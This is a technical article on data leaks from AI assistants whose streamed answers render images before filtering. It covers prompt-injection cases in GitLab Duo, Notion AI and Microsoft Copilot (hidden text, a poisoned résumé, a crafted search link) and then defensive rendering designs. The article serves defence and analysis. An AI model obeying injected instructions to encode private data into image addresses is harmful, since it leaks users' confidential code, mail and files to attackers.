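When an image tag arrives in two parts, neither part is a complete tag, so a filter that searches for complete tags lets both through. The page then joins them, and the browser creates the image. This resembles the file example in MITRE's catalogue, since the check on the first part was correct and the text changed afterwards. The split depends on network and server timing, so the same filter can stop an image in one answer and miss it in the next, which makes a single successful test weak evidence that the filter works.

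Larger chunks make splits less common but do not prevent them. The example tag is 52 characters long, and AWS's *StreamingConfigurations* (2026) gives 50 characters as the default interval at which Bedrock applies its guardrails, so the tag will usually straddle two intervals. A check can then catch it only if it also includes the preceding text.

The toolkit in Mintlify's copy carries 50 tokens over from each chunk to the next by default, which is enough for a short tag. But an address that contains several paragraphs of a letter can run to hundreds of tokens, so the tag can begin long before the carried-over text and end in the next chunk. No single check then covers the whole tag, so the filter would have to treat an unfinished tag as suspicious.

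Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) advises against sanitising chunks in isolation for this reason. Its sample code adds each new chunk to the text received so far, runs DOMPurify on the combined text, and stops the display if DOMPurify has removed anything. Otherwise, it passes the new chunk to the Markdown converter.

The sample code runs its steps in the right order, but it uses DOMPurify's default settings, which keep ordinary image tags. It also gives DOMPurify the Markdown text, in which an image is plain text to an HTML sanitiser. In either case, DOMPurify would have nothing to remove and the check would pass. The code stops the attack that Chrome for Developers uses to introduce it, an image tag with a script attached, but an image that carries data in its address could still get through if the Markdown converter produces images.

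### Deciding late what counts as code

In Markdown, later characters can change the meaning of earlier ones. A single backtick begins inline code only if another backtick follows it. Until the second one arrives, a converter working on the text so far treats the first as an ordinary character and, if it allows raw HTML, treats an HTML tag after it as a real tag. Once the second backtick arrives, the converter reparses the passage as code, and the page shows the tag as text.

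By the time the response is complete, the browser has already created the image. A filter that works from the finished structure has nothing to remove, because the tag is now inside code, and many filters deliberately skip code so that programming answers display correctly. Fenced code blocks are safer than inline code because CommonMark treats everything after an opening fence as code until a closing fence appears.

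Legit Security, which sells software security tools, describes a related problem in GitLab's assistant, Duo. According to its report, *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, Duo's page converted the answer line by line before the full structure was available, so HTML outside a code block could become active too early.

An image written in reference-style Markdown, the notation that defeated the link filter in EchoLeak, stays plain text until the line with its address arrives, perhaps hundreds of tokens later. The converter then turns text the filter has already approved into an image. A filter that examines only new text will miss the image unless it catches the address line.

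### Cleaning up or asking permission after display

Some pages insert the answer as it comes, then run a script that finds and deletes unwanted images. Under the browser rules above, deleting an image does not cancel its fetch. A mutation observer, a browser feature that runs a script when the page changes, reacts faster than a timer. But that script runs as a microtask, so whether it clears the image's address before the fetch starts depends on which microtask the browser runs first.

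An approval step can fail in the same way. A person needs several seconds to read a warning, so the page must keep the markup out of the live document until the user approves it. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes a case in which the assistant in Notion, a service for shared documents, inserted an image into the user's document before asking whether the user trusted the site. By then the browser had already requested the image, so the user's answer made no difference.

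Waiting for the user's approval before saving a change is not enough if the approval box previews the change with its images, because loading them sends the request before the user has decided. The box should show each image's address as text.

### What else the attacker needs

A timing gap supplies only the outbound channel in Willison's trifecta, so the attacker still needs an injection and private data within the assistant's reach. Without an injection, the gap leaks nothing, which may explain how such flaws survive ordinary testing.

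The model must also have read the data before it writes the address, which in the worked example means before it finishes the tag at token 120. Many assistants search the user's files before they begin to answer, so the relevant data is available from the first token. Legit Security found that Duo had the same permissions as the person using it, so it could read that person's private source code.

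If the page has a content security policy (CSP), the attacker also needs a permitted destination. Varonis, like the EchoLeak researchers, needed a permitted Microsoft host that would fetch an outside address on request. Varonis concluded that the attack chain would have failed if any one part had been missing. A team that cannot close a timing gap immediately can still prevent the leak with a strict CSP, as long as no permitted host passes the data on.

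## Three products where the request left first

Security researchers have shown that assistants from GitLab, Notion and Microsoft could send private data to an outside server, despite safeguards that should have prevented it. All three companies have since patched the flaws. Notion's and Microsoft's safeguards acted too late. GitLab's sanitiser seems to have run in time but let an image through anyway, so timing explains less of that leak than the published account suggests.

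### GitLab Duo: instructions hidden in a public project

GitLab is a service where programmers store code and review one another's changes. Its assistant, Duo, runs on Anthropic's Claude and answers questions about that code. Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found that Duo also obeyed instructions left in the material it read. Legit Security reported the flaw to GitLab on 12 February 2025 and published its findings on 22 May.

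Mayraz hid instructions in source code, in commit messages (the notes programmers attach to their changes), and in the descriptions and comments of issues and merge requests (proposals to add changes to a project). Duo followed the instructions in all of these places because it reads the whole page to answer a question. People reading the same page could miss them. For example, GitLab's notation for mathematical formulas allowed white text, and some of the instructions used invisible Unicode characters.

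For the main demonstration, Mayraz put the instruction in the source code of a public project, and a user asked Duo an ordinary question about one of the files. Duo used one of its tools to read a merge request in a private project, which the user had permission to see but did not need to have open. Duo converted the code changes to Base64, which represents any data as letters, digits and a few symbols, and added the result to the address of an image. The browser requested the image, and the researchers decoded the private code from the request.

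The victim in this demonstration was probably Mayraz himself, because the hidden instruction refers to a private project under his own account. Willison reproduces the instruction in writing about Legit Security's report. OECD's *GitLab Duo AI Vulnerability Exposes Source Code and Confidential Data* (2025), an entry in a public monitor of AI incidents, has an AI-generated summary that describes researchers stealing private source code. A reader could easily take this for a theft from GitLab's customers.

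Legit Security adds that the same method could leak confidential issues, including reports of unfixed vulnerabilities. This follows from Duo's permissions, which let it read issues as well as code, but the published evidence shows only source code being leaked.

### How much of the GitLab leak was timing

Duo's page rendered each answer twice. According to GitLab's *feat(DuoChat): Add default markdown renderer for streaming messages*, a code change to the chat window, the browser converted the Markdown as it streamed in, and GitLab's servers supplied finished HTML once the answer was complete. The developers knew the early version could be wrong and were dealing with a fault that made comments inside an unfinished code block appear as headings.

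Mayraz noticed the early conversion when a word's style changed on screen as the answer arrived, and he suspected that a raw HTML tag might become active too. After some experiments, he got the page to display an image by placing an image tag in a link's label.

Legit Security presents this mainly as a timing failure, in which the browser could interpret the HTML before proper sanitisation. Its report also says that Duo passed the answer through DOMPurify, which by default keeps images, forms and links. These two explanations are hard to reconcile. If DOMPurify checked each partial answer before the page inserted it, there was no timing gap, and the image got through because the tag list permitted it. If DOMPurify ran only on the finished answer, the request left before the check, but the image would have passed the check anyway. In either case, running the filter earlier with the same tag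 list would not have protected the data.

Judging by the report, the sanitiser probably processed the markup before the browser did. The researchers first hoped to run a script in the victim's page, but DOMPurify prevented this, so they settled for what they call basic HTML tags. If raw markup had reached the live document before the sanitiser, a script attached to the image should have run. The inference isn't certain, because a CSP that forbids inline scripts would have had the same effect, and the report does not mention one. Willison reads the case differently, and describes the streaming display as a separate bug that could bypass the filter against cross-site scripting.

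Timing may still have helped the attacker get a real image tag into the answer, because a converter that waited for the complete text might have shown the tag as code or ordinary characters. The researchers could have settled this by sending the same answer in one piece and by repeating the attack with images removed from DOMPurify's allowlist, but they report neither test. On the evidence they give, the permitted image tag was enough to cause the leak once it was active, and early conversion at most activated it.

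GitLab's records include two proposals, made for other reasons, that would have closed the hole. In the record titled *Duo Chat*, somebody suggested escaping HTML in Duo's answers because stray tags were breaking the layout. Escaping would have turned the injected image tag into text however fast the answer streamed. *Fix GLQL visualization in Duo chat UI* proposes waiting for the end of the stream, because charts and embedded queries failed when the page processed them before the message had finished. A security reviewer could have learned about the early conversion from either record. Neither carries a date that would show whether GitLab had these complaints before Legit Security's report.

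### What GitLab changed

GitLab (2025) released the fix on 7 April, 54 days after the report, in version 8.12.0 of the package that contains Duo's chat window. The fix leaves links to GitLab's documentation site, gitlab.com and the GitLab installation's own domain unchanged, and neutralises the rest. The developers hard-coded gitlab.com into the list of allowed domains and planned to remove it once another part of GitLab could supply the installation's address.

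GitLab's fix addressed order as well as hosts. Its developer explains that the new code lets sanitisation happen before the page renders links. Because GitLab changed both at once, we cannot tell from the patch's success which change mattered more.

The sources also differ on what it covers. Legit Security says it stops Duo from displaying tags such as images and forms that point outside gitlab.com, and Willison describes a check on the addresses of both links and images. GitLab's description mentions only links, and its test prompts try only HTML links, Markdown links and bare addresses inside and outside code blocks. One test asks Duo to read an issue and put its contents into a link. This closely resembles another report in GitLab's tracker, in which an attacker's comment made Duo print a link containing text from a private issue. That attack needed two questions from the victim. The developers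 may have written the change with the link report in mind and found that it also covered images. The code may well handle images correctly, as the researchers say, but the listed tests would not have caught a mistake there.

Reports conflict on whether GitLab considered the prompt injection itself a security issue. Techzine's *Vulnerability in GitLab assistant enabled code theft* reported that GitLab did not, because the remaining injection did not directly lead to unauthorised access or to running code. Legit Security's report says GitLab acknowledged it as a security issue and confirmed a remedy. Nobody describes the remedy. The restriction on hosts is the part of the fix that outsiders can examine, and it still works if someone finds a new way to plant instructions.

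### Notion AI: a warning that came after the leak

Notion's assistant can edit a team's documents and databases on request. PromptArmor, a company that monitors the AI features of other firms' products, tested it with a hiring tracker and a résumé containing hidden instructions. The instructions were in one-point white type on a white background, with a white image on top, so a person opening the file would have seen a normal résumé.

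The user uploaded a résumé containing hidden instructions and asked the assistant to update the notes on the candidate. Following those instructions, the assistant collected all the text in the tracker, added it to a URL on the attacker's server, and inserted an image with that URL into the Notion page. Notion then asked the user whether to trust the outside site. By then, Notion had already saved the edit and the user's browser had requested the image. The attacker's log held salary expectations, feedback on candidates, details of internal roles and diversity hiring goals.

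One of Notion's two safeguards in this path was a language model that scanned uploaded documents and warned the user if one looked malicious. PromptArmor focused on how the data left rather than on defeating the scan, so its demonstration gives little evidence of how often the scan would have caught a malicious file. PromptArmor argues that an injection could cause the scanning model to classify a file as safe, and that an attacker could instead use a web page, a Notion page or a connected mailbox, none of which Notion appeared to scan.

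The other safeguard, the warning, came too late however quickly the user answered. It displayed the address with the stolen text inside. A careful user who read the warning and refused would have had good reason to think the refusal had protected the tracker.

Notion's assistant saved edits before the user approved them, even when an edit contained an image from an unknown server. Rejecting the edit could not undo the request for that image. Many editors apply suggested changes this way, which is reasonable for text because rejecting a change restores the earlier wording. This version of the timing gap involved no sanitiser or streaming delay, so a reviewer who examined only how the chat window filters its answers would have missed it.

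PromptArmor found a related problem in Notion Mail, where the drafting assistant could put Markdown images from outside sites into a draft. The assistant appeared to see only the Notion sources the user named in the request, so an attacker would have needed the user to mention an untrusted page and a confidential one together, which makes the leak narrower and less likely.

### The closed ticket

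PromptArmor submitted its report on 24 December 2025 through HackerOne, a company that receives and sorts vulnerability reports for other firms. HackerOne acknowledged it that day and asked for a different format, which PromptArmor supplied. The ticket was closed on 29 December with the label "Not Applicable". PromptArmor published on 7 January 2026, and Notion contacted it the same day.

PromptArmor first wrote that Notion had rejected the finding. It added a correction on 8 January, after learning that HackerOne's staff had apparently rejected the report before it reached Notion's own team. Notion confirmed the flaw and put a fix into production on the night of 7 January. The report had been in the system for two weeks, but the fix took less than a day once Notion's team had read it.

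This history is a reason not to treat a closed ticket as evidence that a product is safe. Someone who sorts reports for many companies may not recognise that an image appearing before an approval box is a leak, because the screenshots show an approval box that seems to work.

The later fix is also limited as evidence. PromptArmor's timeline records a remedy for "insecure AI document updates" but gives no date for one in Notion Mail. It does not specify whether Notion now holds an edit until the user approves it, blocks outside images in edits, or restricts image hosts across the whole page. PromptArmor had recommended requiring approval before outside images load and setting a strong CSP. The confirmation that the fix works comes from Notion, and PromptArmor does not describe repeating its attack afterwards.

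### SearchLeak: one click on a Microsoft link

Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search answers questions from a company's email, calendars and files. Dolev Taler of Varonis found a way to make it send out some of that information when an employee clicked a link. Varonis published the attack on 15 June 2026 under the name SearchLeak. Microsoft had listed the flaw as CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June.

The link led to Microsoft's own search page, so a filter that checks where a link goes would not have stopped it. Search pages often accept the search text as part of the address so that people can share or bookmark a search. Copilot treated that text as an instruction as well as a search term. The link's author could therefore tell Copilot what to do in the account of the employee who clicked it, without the employee typing anything.

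Suppose the employee's mailbox holds a message with the title "Your security code 482913", using the code from the earlier example. The sequence then ran like this:

1. The employee clicked the link, and Copilot searched the mailbox as the link instructed.
2. Copilot began to write an answer with an image tag in it. The image's address pointed to Bing, Microsoft's search engine, and contained a further address on the attacker's server. The title of the email was part of that further address.
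3. The page displayed the unfinished answer as HTML, and the browser sent the image request to Bing.
4. Bing's computers contacted the attacker's server to fetch the picture, and the code arrived in the server's log.
5. Copilot finished the answer, and the page wrapped the HTML in a code block, where it was harmless text.

Swapping steps 4 and 5 would not have changed the outcome, because the browser had already sent the title to Bing. The employee might have seen Copilot working for a moment and then a strange answer.

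Varonis demonstrated the attack by extracting the subject line of an email. It says an attacker could have reached whatever the employee could see through Copilot, including the content of messages, meeting notes, and SharePoint and OneDrive files such as salary lists or acquisition plans. Copilot did have that access, but the published request contains only one subject line, and Varonis does not report how much text it extracted in a single answer. Even a subject line can be damaging, because many services put sign-in codes there.

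### Why the attack needed all three weaknesses

Varonis argues that the attack would have failed if any one of three things had been missing: the instruction in the address, the late wrapping, or the fetch by Bing.

If the search page had treated the text in its address only as search terms, the attacker could not have controlled Copilot's answer. Varonis had used the same entry point before. According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, Taler reported a similar attack on the consumer version of Copilot in August 2025, and Microsoft patched it in January 2026. Varonis was surprised that the technique worked in the business product, which was supposed to have more protection. The instruction could perhaps have come from elsewhere, as in EchoLeak, where a hostile email was enough, but Varonis does not report trying that against Enterprise Search.

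With the instruction in place, the attacker still had to get past the wrapping. Varonis published screenshots of the same answer before and after the page wrapped it. The first shows an active image and the second shows plain text, which is the clearest evidence of a timing failure in any of the three cases. The wrapping neutralised the image as soon as it ran, whereas DOMPurify, with its default list in GitLab Duo, would have kept the image whenever it ran.

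The page's CSP was also working. It stopped the browser from loading an image directly from the attacker's server, but it allowed every host under Bing's domain. Bing's search-by-image feature accepts the address of an image, which Bing's servers then fetch themselves, and the page's CSP does not apply to those servers. Without this service, or another permitted one that worked the same way, the early image would have failed to load and the title would have stayed in the browser. EchoLeak had used a preview service in Teams for the same purpose a year earlier, so Microsoft had already seen its own allowlist bypassed this way.

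The claim that the attack needed all three weaknesses is an inference, and Varonis does not describe disabling them one at a time. The inference is sound for the published attack, but fixing one weakness does not necessarily make the other two safe to leave. If Microsoft had only stopped the search page from taking instructions from its URL, an attacker who found another way to inject text could still have exploited the late wrapping and the permitted host.

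The public record does not show which links in the attack chain Microsoft closed. Microsoft's advisory, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), classes the flaw as command injection and states that Microsoft has fully mitigated it on its own servers, with nothing for customers to do. It does not mention the streaming display or Bing. Varonis recommends that developers sanitise the answer when it is displayed and review every permitted host for services that fetch user-supplied addresses.

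### Two severity scores for one flaw

News reports gave SearchLeak different severity scores. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reported a score of 6.5 from Microsoft and 7.5 from the National Vulnerability Database (NVD), which the US standards agency NIST maintains. The Next Web disputed the 7.5, writing that the NVD entry also showed 6.5.

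CVEFeed's *CVE-2026-42824* (2026), which copies the NVD's history of the entry, shows that the NVD received Microsoft's score on 4 June and that NIST added its own on 8 June. Both scores remain in the entry, and The Next Web may have read only Microsoft's.

NIST's *CVSS v3.1 Statistics for Microsoft Corporation as of 06/09/2026* (2026) shows that NIST and Microsoft agree on seven of the eight measures used to rate the flaw under the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). They disagree on the eighth. Microsoft says the attack requires an action by the user, while NIST says it does not, explaining that it had not identified any user interaction.

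The full-point difference comes entirely from that measure. For a flaw of this type, the formula adds a score for impact to a score for ease of exploitation and rounds the sum up to the next tenth. The impact score is 6.42 × 0.56 = 3.595 in both assessments, because both rate the loss of confidentiality as high and record no other damage. For a simple attack over the network that needs no account, the exploitation score is 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85, multiplied by a weight for user interaction.

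| | Microsoft | NIST |
|---|---|---|
| User interaction | Required (weight 0.62) | None (weight 0.85) |
| Impact | 3.595 | 3.595 |
| Ease of exploitation | 2.835 | 3.887 |
| Sum | 6.430 | 7.482 |
| Score | 6.5 | 7.5 |

Microsoft's score fits the published attack better, since nothing happened until the employee clicked. NIST assessed the vulnerability a week before Varonis explained how the attack worked, and the advisory's short description does not mention a click.

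Both assessments also rate the attack's complexity as low, although Varonis calls the late wrapping a race condition. In the same document, NIST raises the complexity of several other Microsoft flaws to high because it identified race conditions in them. Doing the same here would lower Microsoft's score from 6.5 to 5.3, but it would be a mistake because the attacker doesn't have to win a race.

Microsoft gave SearchLeak a medium CVSS score but rated it critical on its own severity scale, the source of the word "critical" in many headlines. Sorting vulnerabilities by score alone would put SearchLeak well below EchoLeak, which scored 9.3, although both could expose an employee's mail and files.

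### The three cases side by side

The table gives what each team demonstrated, which is sometimes less than what it says an attacker could have done.

| | GitLab Duo | Notion AI | SearchLeak |
|---|---|---|---|
| Discoverer | Legit Security | PromptArmor | Varonis |
| Reported to the vendor | 12 February 2025 | 24 December 2025 | Date not published |
| Published | 22 May 2025 | 7 January 2026 | 15 June 2026 |
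| Source of the instruction | Hidden text in a public project | Hidden text in a résumé | The address of a link |
| What the user did | Asked about a file | Uploaded the résumé and asked for an edit | Clicked the link |
| Intended protection | DOMPurify | Scan of uploads, warning about the outside site | Code-block wrapping, CSP |
| Why it failed | The default list kept images, and early conversion may have made the tag active | The software saved the edit before the warning | The wrapping came after streaming, and Bing passed the data on |
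| Data taken | Code changes from a private project | Contents of a hiring tracker | Title of an email |
| Fix | Restricted hosts, released 7 April 2025 | In production 7 January 2026, method not described | On Microsoft's servers by 4 June 2026, method not described |

Only the SearchLeak researchers had to work around a restriction on image hosts. In the GitLab and Notion demonstrations, the browser contacted the outside server directly. A CSP limited to the company's own hosts would have blocked both requests, whatever the order of the other steps, unless the attacker had found a permitted service to relay them, as Bing did in SearchLeak.

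None of the three teams gives a success rate for its injection. Mayraz says he tried several prompts before finding one that triggered the flaw reliably, and the other two teams each describe a successful sequence without saying how many attempts it took. The demonstrations prove that the path from the model's answer to an outside server was open, but they don't show how often an attacker would have got a model to use it.

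### Whether anyone used these flaws

All three teams describe their own demonstrations, and none reports a real victim. SearchLeak has the fullest record. Microsoft's advisory marks the flaw as not exploited, and its scoring data rate working attack code as unproven. Exploit Intel's *CVE-2026-42824* (2026) reproduces an assessment by CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, that also lists exploitation as "none".

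The GitHub repository that CVEFeed lists as a public exploit is an archive of Chinese technology newsletters, created the day after Varonis published. CVEFeed presumably matched it because one of the newsletters mentioned the flaw.

The lack of reported victims is weaker evidence that nobody exploited the flaw in GitLab and Notion than in Microsoft's product. In GitLab and Notion, the stolen data went straight from the user's browser to the attacker, so the vendor's servers would not have received the request. To find attacks, GitLab would have had to search stored answers for images with outside addresses, and Notion would have had to search saved pages and their earlier versions. Neither company has published such a search. Microsoft runs both Copilot and Bing, so its logs could have held the hostile link and the image request that followed. Its advisory does not explain what the company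 examined before marking the flaw as not exploited.

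## Placing the filter ahead of the browser

A page can stream an answer and still protect the user's data, as long as the filter processes every link, image and tag before it reaches the live document. Developers can put the filter on the server, in the page's Markdown parser, in a sanitiser that runs before every update or, in some browsers, in the function that inserts the HTML. Most of an answer is text that cannot start a request, so the filter needs to delay only the small part that can.

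### What waiting costs

The simplest safe design is to filter the complete answer before displaying any of it. With the 600-token answer at 50 tokens a second, the user looks at an empty box for 600 / 50 = 12 seconds.

If the filter instead holds back only links, a 25-token link appears 25 / 50 = 0.5 seconds after its first token arrives, and the text before it is not delayed. Ten such links would cause ten half-second pauses, but the answer would still finish at 12 seconds because the model keeps writing while the filter waits.

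Waiting for the full answer is still reasonable when it is short or nobody is watching it arrive. Nalpas (2026), writing for Chrome's developer site, recommends waiting for short outputs such as image descriptions and for long tasks that run in the background. A 50-token answer takes only a second to complete, and buffering it avoids all the work described below.

### Holding back markup on the server

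The e-commerce company Shopify built a hold-back filter for its assistant, Sidekick, to improve how links look as they arrive. A link that arrives in pieces first appears as brackets and part of an address, then suddenly turns into a link. Shopify's server prevents this by holding back any text that might be the start of a link until the whole link has arrived.

The filter is a state machine, a program that reads one character at a time and keeps track of what it is partway through reading. It holds back text that might be a link until the link is complete, then releases the link as a unit. If a character arrives that could not belong to a link, the filter releases the held text unchanged. Shopify's version also passes each complete link to a function the developer chooses, which can change the link before the browser receives it.

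Here is how such a filter handles a link that the network delivers in three parts:

| Text that arrives | Text the server holds | Text the server sends |
|---|---|---|
| `See the [rep` | `[rep` | `See the ` |
| `ort](https://www.exam` | `[report](https://www.exam` | Nothing |
| `ple.com/q3) first.` | Nothing | The link, if its host passes the check, then ` first.` |

The split between chunks, which defeats a filter that examines each chunk alone, makes no difference here because the filter remembers the earlier part.

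Shopify did not design its filter as a defence, and a security version needs several changes. It has to cover images and HTML tags as well as links, and it must never release suspicious text in its original form. In outline:

```
held = ""
for each character c from the model:
    held = held + c
    if held cannot be the start of a link, image or tag:
        send(escape(held));  held = ""
    else if held is a complete link, image or tag:
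        send(replacement(held));  held = ""
    else if length(held) > LIMIT:
        send(escape(held));  held = ""
when the answer ends, fails or the user stops it:
    send(escape(held))
```

The `replacement` function returns the link if its host is on the allowlist, and otherwise returns only the label as text. It replaces an image with its description and escapes HTML tags. It must also escape the label of any link it keeps, because Markdown allows an image inside a link's label. The researchers who attacked GitLab Duo got their image into the page this way.

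An ordinary letter cannot begin any markup, so the filter sends it at once. The filter holds an exclamation mark until the next character arrives, because only a square bracket there would start an image. It also sends a less-than sign followed by a space without further delay, so text such as "x < y" reads normally.

Reference-style Markdown needs its own rule, because the link and its address can be hundreds of tokens apart. The filter can escape every line that defines an address, which leaves the matching labels as plain text. If an assistant relies on links, developers can instruct it to write each address beside its label instead, and if it fails to do so, the user only loses a link.

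### Markup that never closes

The model may write an opening square bracket and never close it, either by accident or because of injected text. The filter would then hold everything after the bracket until the answer ended, and the user would again wait up to 12 seconds. A cap on the length of the held text limits this delay.

At about four characters a token, the model in the example writes 200 characters a second, so a cap of 400 characters limits each pause to 2 seconds. The 25-token link, at about 100 characters, is well under that cap. A cap of 2,000 characters would allow a pause of 10 seconds, which is hardly better than full buffering. A few genuine links have addresses longer than 400 characters, and users will see those as plain text.

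The cap only limits the delay. It does not prevent leaks, because a six-digit code fits easily in a 60-character address. The protection comes from checking and rewriting the completed markup.

If the filter sends the held text unchanged when it reaches the 400-character cap, the page adds it to the answer, and the rest of the address follows as ordinary text. The page's Markdown converter has no cap, so it receives the complete image markup and creates the image. An attacker could exploit this every time by padding the address past the limit. If the filter escapes the held text instead, the opening bracket loses its meaning, and nothing that arrives later can complete the image.

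Shopify's rule of releasing a false alarm as raw text is risky for the same reason. If the page's converter accepts a link form that the server's state machine rejects, the released text becomes active markup in the browser. EchoLeak got past Microsoft's link filter through this kind of mismatch.

When escaping held text for a Markdown converter, character codes such as `&#91;` for the opening square bracket and `&lt;` for the less-than sign are safer than backslashes. A backslash before a bracket normally makes Markdown show the bracket literally. But if the model has already written a backslash just before the held text, the converter reads the two backslashes as one literal backslash, and the bracket becomes active again. A stray backslash before a character code spoils how the character looks but doesn't make it active.

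Inside a code block, the converter shows escape codes literally, so a filter that escapes everything makes programming answers ugly. A filter that tracks code blocks can leave their contents alone, but it must find the same start and end for every block as the converter does.

### Sending pieces instead of Markdown

Shopify warns that supporting all of Markdown in a hand-written state machine would be a huge undertaking, and suggests a parser generator, a tool that produces a parser from a description of the notation. In a security filter, incomplete support leaves a gap, because any notation the server doesn't recognise passes through to a converter that might recognise it.

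A team that controls both the server and the page can avoid mismatches between two Markdown converters by parsing Markdown only on the server. The server then sends the page labelled pieces, such as "text" with its characters or "link" with its label and checked address. The page inserts text pieces as plain text and creates links only from link pieces.

Shopify's system already does part of this. It sends the answer and other content over one connection as named events, and the page sorts them by name. When Sidekick needs to show live information, the model writes a special link that names what the user wants. The server intercepts the link, fetches the information and sends it as a separate event. Because the application supplies the content, the model never has to write an address for the browser to load. The server must still check that the user is allowed to make each request, since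 injected text could also produce the special link.

A server filter protects every program that receives the stream, including a phone app that the web team didn't write, but not programs that get the answer another way. For example, many assistants save the model's original text and display it when the user reopens the conversation. The team should either save the filtered version or send saved answers through the same filter.

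### A parser that creates only permitted elements

The page can also parse the Markdown itself with a streaming parser, which reads each chunk as it arrives and remembers its position in the text. Chrome for Developers recommends one because ordinary parsers expect a complete document. A single asterisk could begin a list item, italic text or bold text, so a streaming parser waits for more characters to tell which it is. It then adds new elements to the end of the answer without changing the earlier ones.

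This design is safe if the parser builds elements from a short list and treats everything else as text:

```
permitted = { paragraph: 'p', bold: 'strong', italic: 'em',
              list: 'ul', item: 'li', codeblock: 'pre' }

when the parser finds the start of a construct:
    if it is in permitted: add that element and move inside it
when the parser finds the end of a construct:
    if it is in permitted: move back out of the element
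when the parser finds text:
    add it as text
when the parser finds a complete link:
    if its host is permitted: add a link with the label as text
    otherwise: add the label as text
when the parser finds an image:
    add its description as text
```

The page never passes the model's output to the browser's HTML parser. If the output contains an image tag, the page puts the tag in a text node and the user sees it as text. The browser never creates an image that must be removed, so there is no timing gap. A new HTML element that starts requests in some unusual way would not matter either, because the page's own parser creates only the elements on its list.

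A parser that only adds to the end also prevents dangerous late changes of meaning, because it cannot go back and turn an old fragment into an image. But it has to hold ambiguous text a little longer, and it needs the same kind of cap for a backtick or bracket that never closes. Here too the parser should release the overflow as text, which is easy because it only adds text by default.

For links, the parser should read the address with the browser's `URL` function, accept only `https`, and compare the complete host name with the allowlist. Checking only whether the address contains a trusted name would accept `assistant.example.attacker.test`.

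Libraries differ in which elements they build by default. A streaming parser that turns Markdown images into image elements does not stop the six-digit code from leaking through the image address. The developer has to replace the function that creates images, or switch to a library that allows this. Highlighters and diagram tools remain a weakness because they add elements the parser did not create.

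An assistant that needs no formatting can use a much simpler approach. Chrome for Developers recommends adding each chunk with `append()`, which inserts a string as text. Assigning the growing answer to `textContent` is just as safe but slower, because the browser discards and rebuilds the whole text each time. Both methods let the assistant display each chunk without holding it back first.

### Sanitising the whole answer before each update

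A team with an ordinary Markdown converter can keep it and run a sanitiser over everything received so far, each time the page is about to change. Chrome's sample code does this with the Markdown text, in which the sanitiser cannot recognise an image, so the safer order is to convert first:

```
answer = answer + chunk
html   = convertMarkdown(answer)
clean  = sanitise(html, SHORT_LIST)      // returns a tree, not a string
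output.replaceChildren(clean)            // the first step that touches the page
```

The sanitiser examines the same HTML that the page will insert. If a code example's closing backtick has not yet arrived and the converter treats the example as a real image tag, the sanitiser removes the tag from that version of the answer. When the backtick arrives, the next version shows the example as code. The display may flicker, but the browser never creates the image.

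The work grows quickly because every update reprocesses the whole answer so far. Updating after each of 600 tokens means processing 1 + 2 + ... + 600 = 180,300 tokens, about 300 times as many as a single pass at the end. Updating every tenth of a second, or every 5 tokens, reduces this to 36,300, about 60 times as many, and delays each piece by at most a tenth of a second. Doubling the length of the answer still roughly quadruples the work, which may be noticeable for long reports on a low-end phone. Developers can reduce the work by reprocessing only the last paragraph, provided they have disabled reference definitions, which can change earlier paragraphs.

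Chrome for Developers advises stopping the display when the sanitiser removes something, since a cleaned answer is no longer what the model wrote. Stopping may also help as a defence, because an answer that tries to load an image from an unknown host may be the product of an injection, and its other claims may be false too. But the rule gives false alarms when the sanitiser reads raw Markdown. If a user asks how to add a script to a web page, the answer should include a code example with a script tag, and the sanitiser would remove the tag, which would stop the display. Converting the Markdown to HTML first avoids this, because the converter escapes the tag before the sanitiser reads it.

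### An off-screen buffer that still loads images

Nalpas published a newer version of the Chrome advice in April 2026. Her sample code sends the chunks to a streaming parser that builds the answer in a document fragment, a container outside the visible page. The code then displays a sanitised copy of the fragment. According to a comment in the code, the fragment prevents flicker and keeps hostile scripts out of the live page during parsing.

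An image element can start its request before it is added to the page, so the fragment doesn't keep images from loading. If the parser creates an image while it fills the buffer, the browser can contact the attacker's server even if the sanitiser later leaves the image out. The developer can prevent this by having the parser create its elements in a separate, inactive document, such as one made with `document.implementation.createHTMLDocument('')`.

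Nalpas' sample list also allows images and their addresses, so the browser would still load them from the sanitised copy. That suits a page that summarises trusted articles, but it would leak the code in the morning email summary.

The sample also does not match the current standard. It calls a `sanitize()` method and names its list `allowElements`, but WHATWG's description of the sanitiser includes neither. The names probably come from an earlier design. According to Chromium's *Intent to Ship*, an announcement to browser developers, Chrome shipped a previous version of the sanitiser and then withdrew it.

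Under the current standard, the sample would stop with an error at the missing method, and the user would see no answer. That failure is safe, but an obvious repair, replacing the missing call with the standard `setHTML` and keeping the old list, is not. Browsers ignore settings they don't recognise, so the sanitiser would behave as if its configuration were empty, which permits images. The correct name for the list is `elements`.

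### Letting the browser sanitise as it parses

The `setHTML` method combines the sanitiser and the insertion in one step. The page gives it a string of HTML, and the browser sanitises the markup as it parses it, before placing the result inside the chosen element. An assistant can call it with the converted answer at each update:

```
const basic = new Sanitizer({
  elements: ['p', 'strong', 'em', 'ul', 'ol', 'li', 'pre', 'code'],
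  attributes: []
});
output.setHTML(convertMarkdown(answer), { sanitizer: basic });
```

This replaces the last two steps of the previous design, so no other script can alter the HTML between the check and the insertion. Each update still takes more computation than the last, because the page converts and parses the whole answer again.

WHATWG has added streaming versions to the standard. `streamHTML` returns a channel to which the page writes pieces of HTML, and the browser parses, sanitises and inserts them as they arrive:

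```
const writer = output.streamHTML({ sanitizer: basic }).getWriter();
for each piece of HTML:
    await writer.write(piece)
await writer.close()
```

The browser's parser waits for the end of a tag before creating an element, so a tag split between two pieces causes no trouble. The browser need not reparse the earlier part of the answer. The method expects HTML, so a page that receives Markdown also needs a converter that produces HTML in pieces. A similar method, `streamAppendHTML`, adds new content after the element's existing content.

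Both methods remove images when the developer supplies no settings. In an example from Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML*, a heading contains an image tag with a script attached, and the browser keeps the heading but deletes the whole image. WHATWG gives the streaming methods the same sanitiser option, which uses the default list unless the developer changes it, according to Chrome for Developers' *Declarative partial updates* (2026).

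MDN's *Element*, the reference page for `setHTML`, does not include images among the items the method always removes, so a custom list that permits images will let them load.

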